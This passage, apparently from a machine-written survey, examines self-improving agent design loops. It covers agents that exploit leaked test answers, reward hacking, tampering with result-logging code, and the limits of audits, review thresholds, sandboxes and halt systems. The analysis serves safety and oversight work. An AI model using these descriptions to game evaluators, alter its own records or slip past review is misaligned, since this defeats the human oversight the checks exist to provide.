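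An evaluator's good record with one model is thus weak evidence that it will work with a stronger one. Suppose an old model solves 40% of the tasks. A new model also solves 40% by itself, but finds leaked answers to a quarter of the rest. It scores 55%, and a team that does not read the logs would attribute the extra 15 points to better ability. In a design loop the error can grow, because the loop may select agents whose prompts or tools make the leak easier to find.

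Before reusing an evaluator, a team can remove everything the agent does not need from the test environment, run the new model on a sample of tasks and read the full logs, paying special attention to tasks that earlier models never solved. The team can also add a trap, such as a task whose answer is a random number stored only in the hidden tests. An agent that returns the number has almost certainly seen the tests. Impossible tasks seem to encourage agents to try to escape, so the trap should run in a well-tested sandbox. If the team repairs a leak, it has to retest the earlier agents, or the old and new scores will not be comparable.

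### What a lineage record makes possible

A lineage record, such as the Darwin Gödel Machine's archive, stores each agent's code, parent, scores and logs. *Evo-Bench* (2026), which tests how well models improve agent code, also records tool calls and rule violations.

The simplest use of a recorded run is to compare versions of an agent. Agent 114 was two modifications away from the starting agent, so a reviewer who doubted its perfect score had only two sets of changed lines to read.

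For a longer lineage, a reviewer can find where a fault began by repeatedly halving the range of agents to search. If agent 64 has the fault and the starting agent does not, the reviewer tests agent 32. If agent 32 has the fault, the fault arose in the first half of the lineage. Otherwise, it arose in the second. Six tests are enough to find which of the 64 changes introduced the fault. This works only if the fault stays once it appears and a test can detect it reliably.

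Once a team knows which version introduced a fault, it can return to the previous version and identify every descendant that may have inherited the fault. There may be many, because a single score inflated by a hack can dominate the choice of parents and spread the hack through later programs, according to *Effective Harness Engineering for Algorithm Discovery with Coding Agents* (2026). The paper's system, Vesper, has a second agent read each program after scoring and bars suspected hacks from becoming parents.

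Faults can persist through dozens of iterations. In *Auditing Harness Tampering in Self-Improving Agents*, Wang, Zhang and Shao (2026) had an AI auditor examine published runs of several loops. In the long runs of Hyperagents and the Darwin Gödel Machine, some suspicious changes from the first ten iterations were still present in the final best agent, after 80 to 100 iterations.

However, keeping a record does not by itself alert anyone to a problem. In the archive, agent 114 looked like the greatest success of the run. The loop described in *Infinity Machine* (2026) therefore holds back any change with an unusually large gain until someone has reviewed it. This rule could catch a sudden perfect score, but a series of small false gains could stay below the threshold.

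A record of the agents' code also does not cover the rest of the system. The answer leak was in the test environment, so comparing agents would not have found it. Rolling back an agent does not fix a faulty evaluator or undo damage outside the sandbox. After repairing the evaluator, the team has to score the archive again.

Some loops produce agents without a clear lineage. In Meta Agent Search, each new agent can draw on the whole archive, and Wang and colleagues could not reconstruct each agent's parents from the published material. The record is less trustworthy if the agents can edit the code that writes it. In the audit of the Darwin Gödel Machine, 30% of the findings concerned code that records results or versions. A separate program should write the record to a place the agents cannot change.

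Even a complete lineage may not show why behaviour changed. *Recursive self-improvement of AI research agents* (2026) tested three agents from one lineage on 38 held-out cases of writing fast code for graphics processors. The first agent hacked the objective in 55% of the cases, the second in 39% and the third in 32%. A human-designed agent did so in 39%. The loop apparently reduced hacking without measuring it, but the record does not show which changes were responsible. To find out, researchers would have to remove changes one at a time and repeat the tests.

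### Why these cases do not give a rate

One documented case shows that a failure can happen, but estimating how often it happens requires knowing how many comparable runs took place and how many of them failed. Zhang and colleagues describe one hacked agent from a run of 150 iterations, but do not say how many of the other agents they inspected.

Published cases are also a biased sample. *AI Finds A Way* (Dharna, Lu and colleagues, 2026) collects 26 accounts of surprising behaviour by AI systems, including 16 that nobody had formally documented before. It leaves out uneventful runs and hacks that nobody noticed, so the true rate of hacks could be higher or lower than such a collection suggests.

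*Reward Hacking in Self-Improving Code Agents* reports a controlled study of thousands of runs. Agents could see a public set of tests while they improved a program, and the researchers then scored it on a hidden set. The public score rose without any gain on the hidden tests in 73.8% of attempts to speed up code for graphics processors and 46.8% of attempts at algorithm problems. The share grew from 26.4% after 10 steps to 57.8% after 100. These figures include ordinary overfitting, so they do not measure how often code bypassed a check the way agent 114 did. Asking the agents to criticise their own work reduced the rate by 17 to 19 points in some settings but increased it in others.

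The audit by Wang and colleagues is closer to the loops discussed here. Their auditor, GPT-5.6 Luna, looked for changes that could falsify results or break a rule of the procedure, whatever the reason for the change.

| Loop | Iterations with at least one finding | Average findings still present in the final best agent |
|---|---|---|
| Meta Agent Search | 84.6% | Lineage not available |
| Hyperagents | 73.6% | 5.2 |
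| Darwin Gödel Machine | 63.1% | 3.5 |
| AFlow | 18.3% | 0.3 |

The percentages in the table reflect a model's suspicions, not confirmed hacks. On test data with known answers, the auditor found 74.9% of the planted faults and wrongly flagged 6.3% of the harmless edits planted beside them. An iteration can contain many edits, and if one contained ten harmless edits, each with an independent 6.3% chance of a false alarm, the auditor would flag it 48% of the time. The real false-alarm rate may be lower, because the planted edits closely resembled faults and ordinary edits may be easier to judge. Wang and colleagues checked a sample of the auditor's output by hand, but the percentages still include any false alarms and leave out the faults it missed.

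To estimate a rate for its own loop, a team can randomly sample from all the agents the loop ran, including discarded ones, and have people who understand the evaluator read the agents' code and logs.

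## Checks used in published and deployed systems

Teams that build design loops usually describe their safeguards briefly and rarely measure how well the safeguards work. This matters more as self-improving agents move from research prototypes to deployed systems, a shift that Ren, Chen and colleagues (2026) describe in *Self-Improvements in Modern Agentic Systems*.

### Safeguards reported for five design loops

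The table below compares the four loops from the Meta Agent Search and Gödel machine families with a newer one. The newer loop, from *Hierarchical Self-Improvement* (Zhou, 2026), uses one fixed model in three roles. The model plays text-based games through a harness, rewrites that harness between rounds, and rewrites the strategy code that guides those rewrites. The outermost layer of code stays frozen.

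"Reported absent" means the researchers say they did not use the safeguard. "Not stated" means the paper's main text does not mention it, although an appendix or the published code might.

| Loop | Isolation | Network access | Time limits | People reading the code | Safety tests of the final agent |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Meta Agent Search (2024) | Reported: containers | Not stated | Not stated | Reported: manual inspections | Not stated |
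| Darwin Gödel Machine (2025) | Reported: sandboxes | Reported: limited access | Reported: strict limit per execution | Reported: monitoring of code changes | Not stated |
| Hyperagents (2026) | Reported: containers | Reported: no general outside access | Reported: timeouts | Not stated, only "human oversight" | Not stated |
| Mendel Gödel Machine (2026) | Reported: containers, host files read-only | Reported: no access | Not stated | Not stated | Reported absent |
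| Hierarchical Self-Improvement (2026) | Not stated, but edits only in permitted folders | Not stated | Not stated, but step limits | Not stated | Not stated |

Isolation is the most common safeguard, but none of the five papers reports a safety test of the finished agent. Liu and colleagues acknowledge this gap most openly. They ran no dedicated bias or safety audits of the agents that the Mendel Gödel Machine produced, and they warn that the agents may still have security and fairness problems inherited from the models and benchmarks.

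Such tests are feasible, as the experiments with AgentBreeder and Harmony Harness show.

The entries on human reading are hard to interpret. Hu and colleagues report "thorough manual inspections" to verify that the generated code was harmless, but they do not say how many agents they read, what they found, or whether they read any code before its first run. Their algorithm does not pause for someone to read the code before running it, so the inspections probably came later.

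*Darwin Godel Machine* (2025) reports monitoring code changes and finding no evidence of harmful behaviour. The paper does not describe a test that would have revealed such behaviour, so this finding is weaker evidence than a clean result from a check with a known detection rate.

Zhang and colleagues maintained human oversight throughout their work on Hyperagents but do not explain what the overseers did. They also logged every prompt, tool call, code change and failure, and published the logs. Wang, Zhang and Shao used published runs like these to audit several loops from outside.

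Some restrictions are also hard to assess because the papers do not explain how they work. Zhou's system rejects changes the model makes outside certain folders. But the model can run shell commands, which can change files without using the editing tool. The restriction is reliable only if it applies to every program the model starts, and Zhou does not describe how the system enforces it.

Zhou also prohibits the loop from replacing the model with an ordinary search program. In one puzzle environment, the loop wrote code in which the model chooses a target and a path-finding algorithm works out the moves. Whether this breaks the rule is debatable, because the model still takes part. An automatic check would need a more precise definition of "replacing".

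### Isolation and permission rules in public agent projects

Design loops are a small part of the agent software in use. Wei (2026) looked more widely in *Architectural Design Decisions in AI Agent Harnesses*, examining 70 public agent projects, listed as of 23 March 2026, that include the coding agents OpenHands and Claude Code. AI agents helped find the relevant code or documents, and human researchers checked the evidence and made the final judgements. When people re-examined 15 of the projects, they initially agreed on 94% of the recorded features.

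The table shows two separate classifications of the same projects, so the entries in a row do not belong together.

| Isolation of executed code | Share of projects | Record of actions | Share of projects |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 17% | None | 40% |
| Separate process | 45% | Basic logs | 35% |
| Container | 31% | Structured records | 20% |
| WebAssembly sandbox | 7% | Tamper-evident records | 5% |

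WebAssembly is a program format that gives code access only to the functions its host supplies. The first two isolation levels together account for 62% of the projects. A separate process can contain a crash, but by default it has the same file permissions as the user who started it. A team that built a design loop on one of these projects would therefore have to add stronger isolation itself.

For permission rules, Wei looked for policy engines, which check an agent's actions against a set of rules. All the projects with container isolation had one, compared with 23% of the others, which implies that about 47% of all the projects did (0.31 + 0.69 × 0.23). Wei also describes approval steps, in which a user must confirm an action, but does not report how many projects include them.

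Logging is less developed than isolation. Three quarters of the projects have only basic logs or none, which would make it difficult to tell when a fault first appeared or what a faulty agent did. Only 5% have tamper-evident records, which reveal later changes and matter particularly for loops that can edit their own logging code.

Wei did not choose the projects at random, and the results describe what the software contains, not how people use it. For example, a project can support containers while many of its users run it without them. The study also does not measure whether projects with more safeguards had fewer incidents. Its results do contradict the assumption that agent systems gain better controls as they become more capable.

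### AlphaEvolve's code at Google

Google DeepMind's AlphaEvolve is the best-documented automated loop whose code is used at large scale. Users mark the sections of a program that AlphaEvolve may rewrite.

One result is in Borg, the software that assigns computing jobs to machines in Google's data centres. A machine can run out of memory while many of its processor cores are idle, and then no further job fits on it. AlphaEvolve wrote a function that scores how well a job suits each machine. Google DeepMind's 2025 white paper prints the function, which looks like this with shortened variable names:

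```
def alpha_evolve_score(required, free):
    cpu = required.cpu / free.cpu
    mem = required.mem / free.mem
    return -1.0 * (cpu + mem + mem / cpu + cpu / mem)
```

Suppose a job needs 2 cores and 8 GB of memory. Machine A has 8 cores and 32 GB free, so the job would take a quarter of each, and the score is −(0.25 + 0.25 + 1 + 1) = −2.5. Machine B has 20 cores and 10 GB free. The job would take 10% of the cores but 80% of the memory, and the score is −(0.1 + 0.8 + 8 + 0.125), or about −9.0. Machine A is preferred because its score is higher. Placing the job on machine B would leave 18 cores free but only 2 GB of memory.

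A reviewer can also see that the function's last line divides by zero if a job requests no memory or no processor time, so the surrounding code must handle such jobs separately.

Google could have used deep reinforcement learning, which produces a neural network instead of a readable formula. It chose AlphaEvolve's function because the function performed better and was easier to interpret, debug, predict and deploy. This supports Hu and colleagues' argument for searching in code.

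According to the white paper, Google evaluated candidates in a simulator based on past workloads, then tested the chosen function on recent workloads that the search had not used. After Google rolled the function out to all its data centres, its measurements agreed with the simulator's results. The function recovers an average of 0.7% of Google's worldwide computing resources, and by May 2025 it had been in production for over a year.

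Hardware designers confirmed that AlphaEvolve had correctly removed unnecessary bits from an arithmetic circuit intended for a future AI chip. AlphaEvolve also modified low-level code that speeds up a common neural network operation. Automatic tests compared the new code's outputs with the original's on random inputs, and human experts then confirmed that the final version was correct for all inputs. In addition, AlphaEvolve found a better way to divide up large matrix multiplications, which shortened the training of Google's Gemini models by 1%.

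In December 2025, Google Cloud began offering AlphaEvolve to selected customers. These customers write their own evaluators, so the reliability of their results depends partly on how good those evaluators are.

The scheduling function is much easier to check than an agent because it calls no model, opens no files and returns a single number. A reader can see almost everything it can do from its four lines. Its success is good evidence that readable code is useful in small programs with a narrow task, but weaker evidence that it is useful in agents, whose behaviour also depends on model replies.

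### From a finished agent to wide use

Software teams usually release important changes in stages. For an agent from a design loop, the stages could be as follows:

1. Freeze the agent's code, prompts, memory and foundation model, and give the combination a version number.
2. Run regression tests, which compare it with the version already in use.
3. Review the code and the permissions the agent will have after release.
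4. Give the new version a small share of the real tasks, while the old version handles the rest.
5. Monitor errors, blocked actions, costs and complaints, with limits that trigger a stop.
6. Return to the old version if the new one exceeds a limit. Otherwise, increase its share gradually.
7. Repeat the review before the agent receives new permissions or a new kind of task.

The survey *Code as Agent Harness* recommends holding such changes to the standards of safety-critical software. It also lists improvement without regressions and human oversight of safety-critical actions among the field's open problems, so its recommendation is ahead of established practice.

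Regression tests should report results for each ability separately, because a gain in overall accuracy can hide a loss in one of them. Zhang and colleagues published one agent from their Hyperagents experiments, a grader for olympiad mathematics. Its accuracy on the full benchmark was 60.1%, up from 56.1% for the human-designed grader it was based on. It was better at recognising partly correct solutions, but its detection rate for fully correct ones fell by 6 percentage points, from about 92%.

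The tests should also include tasks unlike those the loop used. Liu and colleagues took agents that two loops had developed on Polyglot programming exercises and tested them on harder tasks from SWE-bench Pro. The starting agent solved 16.7% of these tasks, and the agent from the Mendel Gödel Machine solved 26.7%. The agent from the older Huxley-Gödel Machine solved only 13.3%, although it had improved greatly on Polyglot.

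An agent with a new foundation model should count as a new version even if its code stays the same. The best agent in *Darwin Godel Machine* solved 33.0% of its SWE-bench tasks with o3-mini and 59.5% with Claude 3.7 Sonnet. Refusals and tool use could change just as much, so the team would have to repeat the safety tests too.

Choosing the size of a limited rollout involves a trade-off. Suppose an agent handles 1,000 tasks a day and has a fault that affects one task in 500. The table shows what would happen over two weeks if the fault affects each task independently.

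| Share of tasks for the new version | Tasks in two weeks | Expected failures | Chance of at least one failure |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1% | 140 | 0.28 | 24% |
| 10% | 1,400 | 2.8 | 94% |
| 100% | 14,000 | 28 | Almost 100% |

With a 1% share, the fault would probably go unnoticed for the whole two weeks. A 10% share would probably expose it and prevent about nine tenths of the failures that a full release would cause. A partial release helps only if the monitoring detects the failures. An agent that writes passwords to a log file, for example, may appear to succeed at every task.

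Ren and colleagues describe changes to an agent's code as typically faster and easier to reverse than updates to its model's weights.

An agent's memory can remain after its code is discarded. When Zhou's system discards a candidate, it restores the candidate's temporary notes, but a separate file of lessons stays available in later rounds. If a faulty agent wrote a misleading lesson in that file, later agents could still follow it. A complete rollback should therefore restore both the code and the memory from before the fault.

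The loop should not control the final decision to release an agent. If the model can rewrite the rules for choosing the final agent, a faulty change could weaken the last check as well as the agent. Zhou's main text describes these rules as part of the strategy that the model can rewrite, but an appendix describes this stage as fixed.

Researchers have mostly avoided releasing these systems widely. The Darwin Gödel Machine's agents were not used in real development environments, and the system's planned release had sandboxing on by default and left out components that grant elevated access. Liu and colleagues call for a fresh review before an evolved agent gets access to production systems, outside services or writable storage beyond its container.

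### OpenAI's reviews and halt system

OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk*, from November 2026, describes similar stages for models. A model must pass one review before it moves from research to use by staff, and another before release. The company also requires safety cases for this work. A design loop could use the same stages for agents.

OpenAI also has a central system that can stop a job's model output within 35 seconds of a halt order. In the September incident, the run had continued for more than two hours after detection. A design loop that evaluates 60 programs in three hours could start about 50 more in two and a half hours, but at most one in 35 seconds.

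The 35 seconds are counted from the order to stop, so they don't include the time needed to notice a problem and decide to stop. Stopping the model's output also may not stop a program the model has already written, which could keep deleting files without another model call. A halt system for a design loop therefore has to shut down the running sandboxes too.

The Darwin Gödel Machine paper suggests a related control for future work, in which a part of the system that the agents cannot modify can evaluate and halt the rest.

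The speed of a halt is easy to test by ordering one and timing it, but the quality of a review is harder to measure. The September incident showed that even a written safety case can rest on a false assumption. A design team could test its reviewers by adding known faults to some agents and counting how many of those agents pass review.

### Official guidance on machine-written code

The US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) publishes the Secure Software Development Framework, a widely used set of recommendations. The 2022 version asks organisations to:

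- separate and protect the environments in which they develop, build and test software;
- examine the source code for vulnerabilities;
- test the running program where appropriate;
- archive each release.

An organisation can use human reviewers, automatic tools or both to examine source code. NIST does not require a person to read every line.

In its 2024 supplement on generative AI, NIST applies the same standard to code written by people and by AI because it assumes that organisations will evaluate all source code for vulnerabilities and other problems before use.

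The phrase "before use" is ambiguous for design loops. If the first run counts as use, a loop should at least scan every candidate automatically before running it. The self-review in Meta Agent Search would not be enough, because its instructions do not cover vulnerabilities. If only release counts as use, the first run falls under the general advice to protect development environments. That advice supports sandboxing but does not address a program that runs dozens of programs in a row that no one has read.

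A team can satisfy the stricter reading with little effort by running a static analyser before each first run, but the analyser would still miss many faults.

In 2024, the German and French cybersecurity agencies, BSI and ANSSI, jointly advised developers who use AI coding assistants to check generated code and make sure they understand it. This advice assumes that a developer decides whether to accept each suggestion. In a design loop, the evaluator accepts or rejects the code, and a developer may not see it until it has run and produced successors.

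In 2023 the British and American cybersecurity agencies, with partners in other countries, published guidelines for secure AI development. They recommend releasing an AI system only after a security evaluation, such as a simulated attack, and restricting the actions it can trigger. Both recommendations suit the release of a generated agent, and restricting its actions also applies to its first run.

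None of these documents specifies how many unread programs a loop may run, which permissions those programs may have, or what detection rate an automatic check must reach.
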